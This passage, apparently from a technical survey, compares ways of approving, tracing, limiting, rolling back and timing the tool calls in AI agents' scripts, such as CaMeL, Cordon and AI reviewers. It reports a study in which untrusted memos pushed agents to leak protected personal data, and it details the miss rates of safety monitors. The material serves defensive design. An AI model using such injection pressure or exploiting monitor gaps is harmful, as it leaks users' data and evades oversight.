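Chen and colleagues tested Cordon on 45 workflows that each led to an effect forbidden by policy. Without protection, the agent produced the effect in all 45. Existing types of defence stopped 14, detected 5 only afterwards and missed 26. Cordon stopped all 45. In one workflow, a cleanup command's deletions were all inside a permitted folder, so a sandbox would have allowed them. Cordon counted the pending deletions, found more than its policy allowed, and discarded them. A similar limit would stop a script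 that was about to issue 3,000 refunds.

The comparison favours Cordon, because the team built the workflows around the kinds of risk that Cordon targets. The 14 successes are a total across nine types of defence, each tested on five workflows, so they don't show what a combination of defences would catch. All 45 workflows were risky, so the test gives no false positive rate. On ordinary tasks, Cordon didn't measurably lower the agent's scores, which were 90.0% with it and 87.5% without it on part of τ-bench, and 100% both ways on part of Terminal-Bench, a set of command-line tasks. The main experiment used preset approval policies, so it doesn't show whether a person would notice two concert tickets in a list of 40 refunds.

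Because a database can make changes provisionally, a system can check a command's actual effects, including those a list of calls doesn't show, before they become permanent. *Beyond Approved Actions* (2026) describes such a system. In its example, an agent has approval to change the status of invoice 4711, but the database also has a trigger, a stored rule that adds a row to a notifications table whenever an invoice changes. The system compares the provisional changes with the approved ones by operation type, table and number of writes. It finds the extra row and cancels both changes. It also saves the decision, because the command had reported success and later steps might otherwise rely on that report.

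Approving effects once the data is known supplies the information missing from an approval record that names a command but not the workflow behind it. But it works only where the backend can hold changes for inspection. An email, for example, can't be delivered provisionally to a customer's inbox.

### Pausing at each write

Instead of collecting all the writes first, a runtime can stop the script at each one. On Cloudflare's runtime, a developer marks a tool with `requiresApproval: true`, as Cloudflare documents. The runtime doesn't keep the script waiting in memory. It ends the run and later starts the script again from the top, a method known as *abort-and-replay*. If only refunds need approval, the refund script, translated into JavaScript, would run like this:

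1. The script calls `list_charges`. The runtime gives the call a sequence number, logs its arguments and marks it "executing". When the charges arrive, the runtime stores them in the log and marks the call "applied".
2. The script reaches the first refund. The runtime logs the actual charge number and amount as a pending action and aborts the run. The script receives no provisional result.
3. The application shows the pending refund to a person. The log is in durable storage, so the answer can come long after the original request has ended.
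4. After the approval, the runtime runs the same code again from the first line. `list_charges` now returns the stored charges without contacting the payment system. The first refund goes through, the first email goes out, and the run aborts at the second refund.
5. This repeats until the script finishes. For 40 refunds, it takes 40 approvals and 41 passes through the code.

Replay works only if every pass makes the same calls in the same order. Cloudflare's runtime compares each call with the log and ends the run with a replay-divergence error if the tool or arguments at a sequence number have changed. Suppose line 6 put the current time into the email. The second pass would send "We refunded 20 at 10:02", and the third pass would try to replay that call with "10:15", so the run would end with one customer refunded and 39 waiting. A script can avoid this by wrapping the clock reading in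 `codemode.step()`, which records the value once and returns it on later passes.

Calls that may pause must also run one after another. If a script starts several refunds at once with `Promise.all()`, they can reach the runtime in a different order on each pass. Refund A might be number 2 on the first pass and number 3 on the next. The comparison makes the run fail in that case, so that an approval given for A can't release B.

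The stored results keep the data fixed while people decide, so all 40 approvals refer to the same list of charges, but the list gets older with every approval. A developer can tell the runtime to repeat a read on each pass instead, but then a new duplicate charge near the top of the list would become the first refund. That refund wouldn't match the log, so the run would end. Cloudflare doesn't allow this setting for tools that need approval, because a replay could then issue an approved refund twice. Each stored value is also limited to a million characters. At 200 characters per charge, a list of more than 5,000 charges would exceed the limit, and the run would fail.

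Since a rejection ends the run, the reviewer can't skip one refund and continue. If the reviewer rejects the 30th refund, which is for concert tickets, the first 29 refunds stand and the ten remaining customers don't get refunds.

The shop could avoid most of these problems by using a tool that takes the whole list, such as `refund_batch(duplicates)`, and requiring approval only for that tool. The script would pause once, with all 40 refunds in the arguments, and a rejection at that point would leave nothing to undo. A batch tool hides the number of refunds from a reviewer who has only the script's text, but the number is known by the time the script pauses.

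### Keeping writes out of scripts

OpenAI's runtime can also pause. For tools on MCP servers, the `require_approval` setting can hold the program until the developer approves the call. For tools that the developer's own application runs, the application can ask a person for approval before it returns a result. OpenAI also recommends making calls *idempotent* where possible, so that repeating a call has no further effect. Otherwise, a retry or replay might refund a customer twice.

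The company still advises keeping writes out of scripts by default. Its sample instructions to the model prohibit actions with side effects in scripts and reserve direct calls for judgement, approval and final validation. The application must approve high-impact actions whether they come from a script or a direct call.

Under this advice, the script serves as the preview by printing the 40 duplicates and stopping. Unlike any automatic preview, this gives the model a chance to recognise the concert tickets, because it reads the duplicates before it requests any refund.

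Handing the data to the model has two drawbacks. Any instruction hidden in the printed data can influence what the model does next. The model also has to copy 40 charge numbers and amounts into new calls, so software can no longer trace those values from the payment system to the refund. *PACE* (2026), which traces values through an agent's tool calls, covers only a narrow range of cases because its identifiers are lost when values pass through the model. A gate can still compare each copied number with the original list, but only if it can identify that list.

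The advice therefore suits writes that each need fresh judgement. When 40 refunds fall under one rule, a reviewer can see the same list and approve it once through `refund_batch`, which keeps the values in code.

### CaMeL's rules about where values came from

A shop that doesn't want to ask a person every month can have software apply a policy at each call. CaMeL, which Debenedetti and colleagues presented in March 2025, does this for scripts. A privileged language model writes the program. A second, quarantined model extracts values from untrusted text, such as the account number from an invoice, but can't give the first model instructions. A special interpreter runs the program and makes the tool calls.

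*CaMeLoT* (2026), a later system that adds static verification, explains how the interpreter tracks data. It attaches two facts to every value: its *sources*, meaning where it came from, and its *readers*, meaning who may see it. When a program combines *x*₁, …, *x*ₙ into a new value *y*, the sources add up like labels in a static analysis. The cautious rule for readers is

readers(*y*) = readers(*x*₁) ∩ … ∩ readers(*x*ₙ)

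A policy is an ordinary Python function. It receives the requested call, its arguments and the facts attached to them, and returns "allow" or "deny". For the shop's emails, a policy could require that

recipient ∈ readers(text)

Suppose only the shop and the customer concerned may read a charge record. In the faulty script that sends all 40 emails to the first customer, the second email contains the second customer's amount. The first customer may not read that amount, so the policy denies the call. Static labels for kinds of data missed this error. However, the second customer's refund has already gone through, because line 5 issues it before line 6 tries to send the email.

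Debenedetti and colleagues report that CaMeL solved 77% of AgentDojo's tasks, compared with 84% for an undefended system. CaMeL's security comes from its interpreter and policies, so it doesn't depend on the model recognising an attack. But a policy about origins accepts any value from the right source. The concert tickets would pass such a policy, because their charge numbers and amounts come from `list_charges`, just like those of a real duplicate.

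*The LLMbda Calculus* (2026) later found weaknesses in the tracking. When a program fails, CaMeL has the model write a new one, and this retry loop runs outside the interpreter. Each new attempt therefore starts with a clean record, even though it depends on error messages from the previous attempt. CaMeL censors those messages to limit the risk, but without a formal guarantee. The paper also found unexpected behaviour in how the interpreter passes its labels on. The paper's own interpreter comes with a proof that rules out this type of flaw.

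*Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026) extends the method to several agents. When one agent calls another, it passes instructions and data as separate arguments. The interpreter rejects any instruction that depends on a tool's output, and the data keeps the record of its origins when it is passed. If line 6 passed a customer's note to a support agent, the note would have to go in the data argument.

Odersky and colleagues point out that CaMeL also restricts scripts to a subset of Python in which they can't define their own functions. They regard run-time policies like CaMeL's as a complement to static guarantees, since a compiler can check all paths through the code but can't determine the actual recipient.

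### Provenance checks on arguments

Knowing where a value came from (its *provenance*) isn't enough to decide whether a script may send it to a particular place. Dong, Lu and colleagues (2026), in *The Claws in Plain Sight*, studied agents that were allowed to read personal data but not to pass it on. Each agent had to prepare a product offer from a profile with a person's age, gender, income bracket and occupation. In most sessions, an untrusted memo pressured the agent to include those details, for instance by presenting them as mandatory for an audit.

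The agent copied at least one protected detail into its tool call in 40 of the 90 sessions where its instructions restricted the use of this data. The strictest instructions said that the rule took precedence over any memo, but the agent still leaked data in eight of the 30 sessions that used them. The true numbers may be higher, because the researchers could recover no arguments from 11 of the 120 total sessions, so those could not be counted as leaks. The sample is small and covers one invented task, but it shows that a rule in the prompt doesn't reliably stop an agent from leaking protected data.

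Dong and colleagues therefore built a monitor that checks the finished arguments before the call runs. Its decision depends on five things:

allow(source, data, purpose, recipient, field)

The purpose comes from the active task and the recipient from the tool's registration, so nothing the model writes can change either. The monitor blocks a call if any value isn't allowed in its field. In other configurations, it can remove the value, replace it or ask a person. An approval applies to a hash of the entire call, so changing any argument invalidates the approval.

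The monitor recognises exact copies and the results of registered calculations, but would miss paraphrases and the results of unregistered calculations. For example, the shop could register the function that shortens a card number to its last four digits, and allow the result in emails to the cardholder but not in messages to an advertising service. In a small test on 12 recorded sessions, the monitor blocked all 12 forbidden calls. In a second test on the same sessions, it blocked nine forbidden calls and let three permitted ones through. These results confirm that the mechanism works as designed, but give little indication of how often it would fail in real use.

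A value must also keep its original provenance when it is reused. Suppose a support ticket contains a stranger's address, and the agent uses it in a harmless search of the customer database. The address then also appears in the record of a successful, authorised call. The system in *When Tool Outputs Become Commands* does not trust the address just because it appears there. Otherwise, an attacker could make a value trusted by getting the agent to use it once in a harmless call.

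### Undoing instead of predicting

Patil and colleagues made an early case for letting an agent act first and having people judge the result afterwards, provided that the user can undo the action or the possible damage is small. They argue that people can often judge the result of an action more easily than the code that will produce it. They concede that in some cases, such as an audit report, the process matters more than the result.

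Their system, GoEx, has two ways to undo a change to a database:

- **Reversal.** A language model writes a second command that is meant to cancel the first. GoEx can test the pair on a small artificial database, but this doesn't guarantee that the reversal will work on the real one.
- **Versioning.** The database keeps the change provisional until the user confirms it. This does guarantee a clean return to the old state, but it costs more, and other users may have to wait for the transaction to finish.

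When an action can't be undone, GoEx limits the damage by restricting access. For example, it could let an agent read emails but not send them. That restriction would stop the refund script at line 6, after the first refund.

Rollback works best on data the runtime controls. Chen and colleagues compared Cordon with Git, the standard tool for tracking versions of files, in three trials of each of five kinds of failed agent step. Cordon restored everything, and the task could continue in all 15 trials. Git's ordinary restore command typically left 73 differences behind, mainly because it ignores untracked files, and the task could continue in none of the trials. A more thorough cleanup succeeded in 12 trials and failed in the other three, where the agent had changed a file's permissions.

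Cloudflare's rollback also covers outside services, but there it can only compensate for effects rather than undo them. If one reversal fails, the runtime continues with the next. It marks the whole run as "rolled back" if at least one reversal succeeded.

For the refund script, the label "rolled back" could be badly misleading. Suppose the shop writes a function that reverses refunds by charging the customer again, but none for emails. If 39 of the 40 new charges fail because the cards have expired or the banks refuse them, the run still counts as rolled back. All 40 customers have an email promising a refund, and one of them has been charged again.

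### What the calls add up to

If the shop allows refunds of up to 40 dollars, a script can issue 3,000 refunds of 20 dollars each and pay out 60,000 dollars without breaking the rule. The gate therefore needs a running total. With *n* refunds and *s* dollars already paid, it would allow another refund of *a* dollars only if

*n* + 1 ≤ 50 and *s* + *a* ≤ 2,000

Surapani and colleagues argue that systems should decide on authorisation at every call, yet they name limits on combined effects as one of the two main gaps in current designs. Adding up the effects is easy, but deciding which calls to count together is hard. If the count restarts with every script, a model whose script stops at the 50th refund can write another and issue 50 more. The shop would have to count refunds per month or per task, across all scripts and agents.

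A running limit also takes effect only after the script has issued some refunds. In the month with 3,000 apparent duplicates, it stops the script after 50 refunds, all of which may be wrong. A preview would show the total of 3,000 before the script issued any refunds.

### Scripts that stop halfway

The simplest way to handle a refusal during a run is to end the script, as Cloudflare's runtime does. If the model then writes a corrected version, that version will list the charges again and may find the 29 duplicates that were already refunded. Those customers would then get their money twice, unless the payment system rejects repeated refunds or the new script checks which charges the shop has already refunded.

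The gate could instead refuse the single call and let the script continue. But the refund script ignores the result of line 5. If a refusal came back as an ordinary value, line 6 would still run and tell the customer about a refund that never happened. The gate has to raise an error, and the script has to handle it:

```python
for c in duplicates:
    try:
        await issue_refund(charge=c["id"], amount=c["amount"])
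    except Refused:
        continue
    await send_email(to=c["email"], text=f"We refunded {c['amount']}.")
```

This version skips the concert tickets and still serves the other 39 customers. But because a script can continue after a refusal, a harmful script could try different amounts until the gate accepts one. A limit on the number of refusals per run would prevent that.

In *Guardrails as Infrastructure*, Sigdel and Baral (2026) measured how strict checks on each tool call affect tasks. They replayed prepared sequences of calls without a language model and inserted forbidden calls and technical faults, including writes that only partly succeeded. Checking the format of calls, or allowing and forbidding tools by name, stopped none of the forbidden calls. Adding limits on arguments and budgets stopped 60%, and adding approvals and the removal of secrets from outputs raised this to 68%.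 The share of tasks completed fell from 36% without checks to 7% under the strictest policy, although the checks wrongly blocked only 6.7% of harmless calls. The percentages won't carry over to a real shop, because the tasks were artificial and often failed even without checks, but the results show that a policy that wrongly blocks few harmless calls can still prevent most tasks from finishing.

A preview reduces this risk because any refusal comes before the first write, but carrying out the approved list still takes many steps. If the connection fails after the 29th refund, the shop is still left with the month's refunds half-finished. Cordon records the status of every effect in its outbox and, after a crash, resends one only if it has evidence that the earlier attempt didn't complete. Without that evidence, somebody has to ask the payment company whether the refund went through.

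## What the checks cost in time

Developers use scripts partly because they are faster than direct calls, and every check reduces the time saved. The reduction depends on how long the check takes and how often it runs. The refund script needs one review if somebody approves it as a whole, but 81 if a gate examines every call.

### A timing model

Suppose a job needs *n* tool calls. Each call takes *t* seconds, each model turn takes *m* seconds, and writing the script takes *w* seconds. Reviewing the whole script takes *R* seconds, and reviewing one call takes *r* seconds. Every version of the job ends with one more model turn to reply to the user.

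direct calls = *n*(*m* + *t*) + *m*

script without review = *w* + *nt* + *m*

script reviewed once = *w* + *R* + *nt* + *m*

script reviewed at every call = *w* + *n*(*t* + *r*) + *m*

The script therefore saves *nm* − *w* seconds. Reviewing every call uses up the whole saving when *nr* = *nm* − *w*, or

*r* = *m* − *w*/*n*

In a long script, *w*/*n* is close to zero, so per-call review saves time overall only if reviewing a call takes less time than the model turn the call replaces.

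*TraceLab* (2026), a study of coding agents that the researchers used in their own daily work, found that a model turn took a median of about 5 seconds and a tool call 0.3 seconds. The example assumes these values, though the shop's agent might be faster or slower, and assumes that writing the script takes 10 seconds. For both *R* and *r*, it assumes 3.2 seconds, the median time Wu and colleagues' AI reviewer took to judge a shell command.

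| Refund script, 81 calls | Calculation | Seconds |
|---|---|---|
| Direct calls | 81 × 5.3 + 5 | 434.3 |
| Script without review | 10 + 81 × 0.3 + 5 | 39.3 |
| Script reviewed once | 39.3 + 3.2 | 42.5 |
| Script reviewed at every call | 39.3 + 81 × 3.2 | 298.5 |

The script saves 395 seconds. One review uses almost none of that time, but 81 reviews use about two thirds of it. With 81 reviews, the script breaks even if each review takes an average of 4.9 seconds.

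This compares a reviewed script with unreviewed direct calls. If the shop also reviewed direct calls, they would take 694 seconds, and the script with per-call review would still be 395 seconds faster. The time per-call review takes is therefore no reason to go back to direct calls.

The saving would be much smaller if the model bundled its direct calls. Suppose it requested all 40 refunds in one response and all 40 emails in the next. At an assumed 40 tokens (word pieces) per call and 40 tokens per second, the job would take about 91 seconds, and the break-even point would fall to 0.6 seconds per review. However, most model turns in *TraceLab*'s data contained only one tool call, and very large bundles can fail. *The Bitter Lesson of Tool Calling* (Patel, Sen and colleagues, 2026) found that Claude Sonnet 5 began to leave out calls when a response needed more than about 70, whereas the scripts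 it wrote still made all 100 calls.

Short scripts save little or no time. With the assumed values, a script with two calls takes exactly as long as two direct calls, so any review of it adds delay. Mak and colleagues found only about two calls per program in their tests.

### Published savings

Liu, Li and colleagues (2026), in *Beyond Static Endpoints*, use a similar model to decide whether a task should run as a program. Their programs run on the server next to the services, so they also save network trips. With *c* for the network round trip, *d* for the agent's decision time and *b* for the time to build the program, the predicted saving is

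(*n* − 1)(*c* + *d*) − *b*

The system reduced the average time on three complex workflows from 30.2 to 17.9 seconds, and the time on a workflow that involved several services from 52.7 to 24.5 seconds. The 12 seconds saved on the complex workflows would be enough for only three reviews at 3.2 seconds each.

The comparison agent replanned before every call. Liu and colleagues also built a leaner agent that makes a rough plan once and then fills in one call at a time. With eight calls and network round trips of up to 100 milliseconds, the leaner agent took 14.5 to 15.3 seconds and the program took 15.5 to 15.6. The program was clearly faster only when round trips took a second or more. On OpenAI's and Anthropic's runtimes, most calls travel to the developer's application and back, so scripts there reduce the number of model turns but not the number of those trips.

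Anthropic estimates that a script with 20 or more calls removes at least 19 model turns, each taking hundreds of milliseconds to seconds. On complex research tasks, average token use fell by 37%, from 43,588 to 27,297. The company did not publish total running times. In the refund example, model turns account for 94% of the time that direct calls take. That is plausible for a large model, since *ToolSpec* (2026) found that generating tool calls took up to 96% of the total time with a 72-billion-parameter model.

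### How long a review takes

Checks that apply written rules usually take too little time to matter. *AgentWall* (2026) describes a rule checker that took 0.2 milliseconds on average over nine test calls. *ActPlane* (2026) enforces 32 rules inside the operating system, and this added 1.9% to the running time of 68 recorded agent actions. Even compiling a script in TACIT takes less than a second.

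AI reviewers take longer, partly because they write more. In *Safety Sentry* (2026), Llama Guard 3, a small safety model, took 0.15 seconds to output "safe" or "unsafe". The paper's own reviewer took 1.57 seconds because it also writes a reason and sometimes a question for the user. The agent itself took 3.75 seconds per step. *StepGuard* (2026) reports 0.6 seconds per reviewed call, or 7% of the total time for tasks with about four calls each.

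*AgentBouncer* was slower. Its reviewer made 7.8 decisions per task on average and lengthened the task from 60 to 108 seconds, which works out at about 6 seconds per decision. The table applies these times to the refund script:

| Reviewer | Seconds per check | Seconds added by 81 checks |
|---|---|---|
| *AgentWall*, written rules | 0.0002 | 0.02 |
| Llama Guard 3, verdict only | 0.15 | 12 |
| *StepGuard* | 0.6 | 49 |
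| *Safety Sentry* | 1.57 | 127 |
| Wu and colleagues | 3.2 | 259 |
| *AgentBouncer* | about 6 | about 500 |

Only the last of these would take longer than the 395 seconds the script saves. The times come from different hardware, models and tasks, so they don't show which design is fastest. But a comparison in *AgentBouncer* shows that frequent reviews can add a lot of time. An earlier system, AgentSentinel, made 63.7 model calls per task and increased the running time by 356%.

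Trębacz and colleagues monitor the delay that Auto-review adds to Codex but did not publish the figures. SyFI TraceLab, which hosts updated data from the *TraceLab* project, gives an upper bound on the delay. Across 338,000 Codex tool calls, the time not spent running the tool had a median of 0.16 seconds and exceeded 10.2 seconds in the slowest 1% of calls. This time includes starting the command line and scheduling, as well as any approval by a person or an AI reviewer. Most Codex actions need no approval, so the median is a poor measure of the reviewer's speed.

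A short delay per call can also be misleading. The strictest rules that Sigdel and Baral tested cut the 95th-percentile delay from 14.65 to 7.04 milliseconds, mainly by blocking calls early and limiting retries, but they also kept most tasks from finishing.

### Reviewers with two stages

A two-stage reviewer saves time by reasoning only about actions that a quick check has flagged. If the quick check takes *t*₁ seconds, the reasoning takes *t*₂ seconds and the quick check flags a share *f* of the actions, then

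expected time per action = *t*₁ + *f* × *t*₂

The first stage of Anthropic's classifier flagged 8.5% of harmless actions. Anthropic hasn't published the time either stage takes, so we assume 0.3 seconds for the first and 4 seconds for the second. The expected time for a harmless action is 0.3 + 0.085 × 4 = 0.64 seconds. Checking 81 harmless calls would take about 52 seconds, compared with 324 if the reviewer reasoned about every call.

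The refund script probably wouldn't take 52 seconds, though, because its calls are so similar. If the first stage flagged none of them, the reviews would take 24 seconds. If it flagged all the refunds and emails, they would take 344 seconds. A quick check tuned to block when in doubt is also more likely to flag a refund than to flag a typical coding command. Reviewing the script as a single action would take at most 4.3 seconds.

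*Agent-Sentry* (2026) applies the same idea with even faster first checks. Rules and a small statistical model settle 96.9% of decisions in a few milliseconds, and a language model handles the rest in 1.2 seconds each. An average run has two actions to check, so the language model adds about 2 × 0.031 × 1.2 = 0.07 seconds per run. If it checked both actions, it would add 2.4 seconds.

### Waiting for a person

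For a human gate, the expected delay per action is

expected delay = chance of being asked × average waiting time

Little published data exists on how long people take to answer permission prompts. *TraceLab* measured a related delay, the time until the user's next message. The median was 1.4 minutes, but 10% of waits lasted more than 20 minutes, and the average was 47 minutes because users sometimes left sessions open for hours. These waits include the time users spent reading results and deciding what to do next, so a simple approval might be faster.

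In a browser game about approving an agent's commands under time pressure, players took roughly six seconds per decision and missed a third of the threats. The six-second estimate is based on about 409,000 decisions in 40,000 games, each lasting 60 seconds according to scalex.dev's *Suffering from Agent Permission Fatigue?*.

If the shop's reviewer approves the refund script once, after an assumed wait of 84 seconds (*TraceLab*'s median), the job takes 123 seconds, which is still much faster than unreviewed direct calls. The average wait is 47 minutes, which would make the job much slower than those calls. If the reviewer has to approve each of the 80 refunds and emails, the approvals take 480 seconds even at the game's pace, which is more time than the script saved.

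A long wait can also end the run, because Anthropic's container times out after about four minutes. Waits matter most when nobody is there to answer a prompt. In *Running auto mode in production* (Vorwerck, 2026), an engineer at the self-driving company Nuro describes an agent that worked from 10 p.m. until 5 a.m. A single permission prompt at 10:05 could have stopped it until morning.

### How much AI reviewers reduce interruptions

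Trębacz and colleagues published an illustrative snapshot of Codex use at OpenAI, scaled to 10,000 actions. 9,280 actions stayed inside the sandbox and needed no review. Auto-review examined the other 720, approved 713 and denied seven. The agent found a safer way to continue after four of the denials, and stopped to ask the user after the other three. Manual mode would have interrupted someone for all 720 actions, so auto-review reduced interruptions 240-fold in this snapshot. OpenAI puts the general figure at roughly 200-fold.

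The two formulas show what this could mean in time, with an assumed 3.2 seconds per AI review and 84 seconds per human answer:

- Manual approval: 720 × 84 seconds = 16.8 hours
- AI reviewer: 720 × 3.2 + 3 × 84 seconds = 43 minutes

About 90% of the remaining delay would come from the AI reviewer, so speeding it up would help more than removing the last three prompts. The result depends heavily on the sandbox, which exempted 93% of the actions. The refund script would benefit much less, because 80 of its 81 calls have effects outside the sandbox.

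Vorwerck reports that Claude Code works nine times longer between interruptions in auto mode than under the previous default. This isn't directly comparable with OpenAI's figure, which counts stops for approval, because the time between interruptions may also depend on how soon the agent finishes its task or needs to ask a question.

Anthropic says that auto mode users on its Team and Enterprise plans submit about 25% more pull requests. But those users chose the mode, and people who were already productive may have been more likely to try it.

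Some customers choose to keep certain prompts. The platform engineering manager at Garner Health, a healthcare technology company, set auto mode not to approve emails or Slack messages to other people. The same rule at the shop would produce 40 prompts, taking four minutes at the game's pace or 56 minutes at 84 seconds each. A tool that sends the whole batch after one approval would save most of that time.

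### How false positives add up

Wrong blocks also add delay, and longer scripts are more likely to hit one. If a gate wrongly blocks a share *p* of harmless calls and its errors are independent, the chance of at least one wrong block in *n* harmless calls is 1 − (1 − *p*)ⁿ. Anthropic reported a rate of 0.4% for its full classifier, which gives a script with 50 harmless calls a chance of 1 − 0.996⁵⁰, or about 18%.

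| Harmless calls in the script | Both stages, *p* = 0.4% | Fast stage alone, *p* = 8.5% |
|---|---|---|
| 2 | 0.8% | 16% |
| 10 | 4% | 59% |
| 50 | 18% | 99% |
| 80 | 27% | 99.9% |

The fast stage alone would be nearly unusable for checking long scripts call by call. The true figures for the refund script are probably lower because its calls are so similar.

According to Anthropic, a wrong block in an ordinary session usually leads to a single retry. That would take about one model turn, or 5 seconds. Recovering from a wrong block inside the refund script takes longer, because the model needs an assumed 10 seconds to write a new version, which also has to skip the customers who already have their refunds.

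Block rates from real use don't show how many blocks were wrong. At the payroll company Gusto, auto mode denied at least one action in about 10% of sessions since mid-May. Vorwerck treats this as evidence that the classifier is useful and doesn't slow down legitimate tasks. But at a false positive rate of 0.4%, a session with 26 harmless reviewed actions has a 10% chance of a wrong block. A Gusto engineer said the blocks he saw made sense, but someone would have to judge a sample of blocks to find out how many were wrong.

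### Ways to reduce the delay

Giving the reviewer better evidence can save time. Wu and colleagues' reviewer took a median of 3.2 seconds with a report of a command's observed effects and 3.3 seconds without one. With the report, the 95th percentile fell from 11.4 to 6.4 seconds. Running the command in a sandbox to produce the report added about 0.5 seconds if the reviewer allowed the command and 1.5 seconds if it didn't. In one test, Wu and colleagues paired each dangerous task with a harmless one that used the same command. The report reduced wrong blocks on the harmless tasks from 61.8% to 1.0%, which would also save many retries. The method works only when a sandbox can contain the command's effects, so the shop would have to use a preview instead.

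A smaller model is faster but may judge less well. When Wu and colleagues gave the same evidence to a weaker reviewer, the share of dangerous tasks that ended in harm rose from 7.8% to 33.3%, and wrong blocks rose from 1.0% to 4.9%. *AgentBouncer* suggests a small model trained for reviewing, which might avoid some of this loss.

Caching saves the reviewer from processing the same text twice, as in the two stages of Anthropic's classifier. But both stages see the same evidence, so the second can't make up for a fact missing from the first. The agent's own cache can also expire while it waits for a person. In *TraceLab*'s data, cache misses began after five idle minutes, and after an hour the agent almost always had to process its context again.

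Exempting harmless tools from review works well for scripts that mostly read. In Anthropic's example of a budget check on 20 employees, every call is a read, so exempting reads would remove all the reviews. In the refund script, it would remove one of 81 reviews. The exemption also means nobody checks whether a read discloses data through its arguments.

The shop could also approve the refund script once and reuse it every month, with a hash of the code to show whether anyone had changed it. Tying the approval only to a familiar name would be risky, since players of scalex.dev's game often missed threats hidden behind such names. For a monthly job, reuse saves only one approval each time, and the shop loses the chance to notice a run with 3,000 refunds instead of 40. Reuse makes more sense for a script that runs every few minutes and has limits on its effects.

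A runtime can reduce the delay by running reads during the review and holding the first write until the reviewer decides. The review and the reads then take as long as the slower of the two, instead of their sum. With 20 reads of 0.3 seconds each, a review of 3.2 seconds would add no delay. The refund script has only one read, so it would save 0.3 seconds. The runtime needs a way to identify calls that are safe to start early, which the effect declarations that Kovalenko and Redchych use would provide. But if the reviewer rejects the script, the reads have already happened, including any that disclosed data.

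Reviews can also run in parallel. If the script requested all 40 refunds together and then all 40 emails, the reviews could take three rounds of 3.2 seconds, or about 10 seconds instead of 259. Cloudflare's runtime doesn't allow parallel requests for calls that may pause. A limit on total refunds would have to count those still under review, or several could pass together and exceed it. The reviewer would also need enough capacity to handle many requests at once. *Persona Guardrail* (2026) describes a safety model that completed 90% of its checks within 100 milliseconds, but at 30 requests per second the slowest 1% took longer.

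While a person decides, the agent can work on something else. *Agent-First Tool API* (2026) describes a system that saves the complete request, returns an approval number to the agent and resumes the request when the answer arrives. The saved request keeps its arguments, so the shop's reviewer can be sure which 40 refunds the approval covers. But before it pays the refunds, the shop still has to check that the charges haven't changed.
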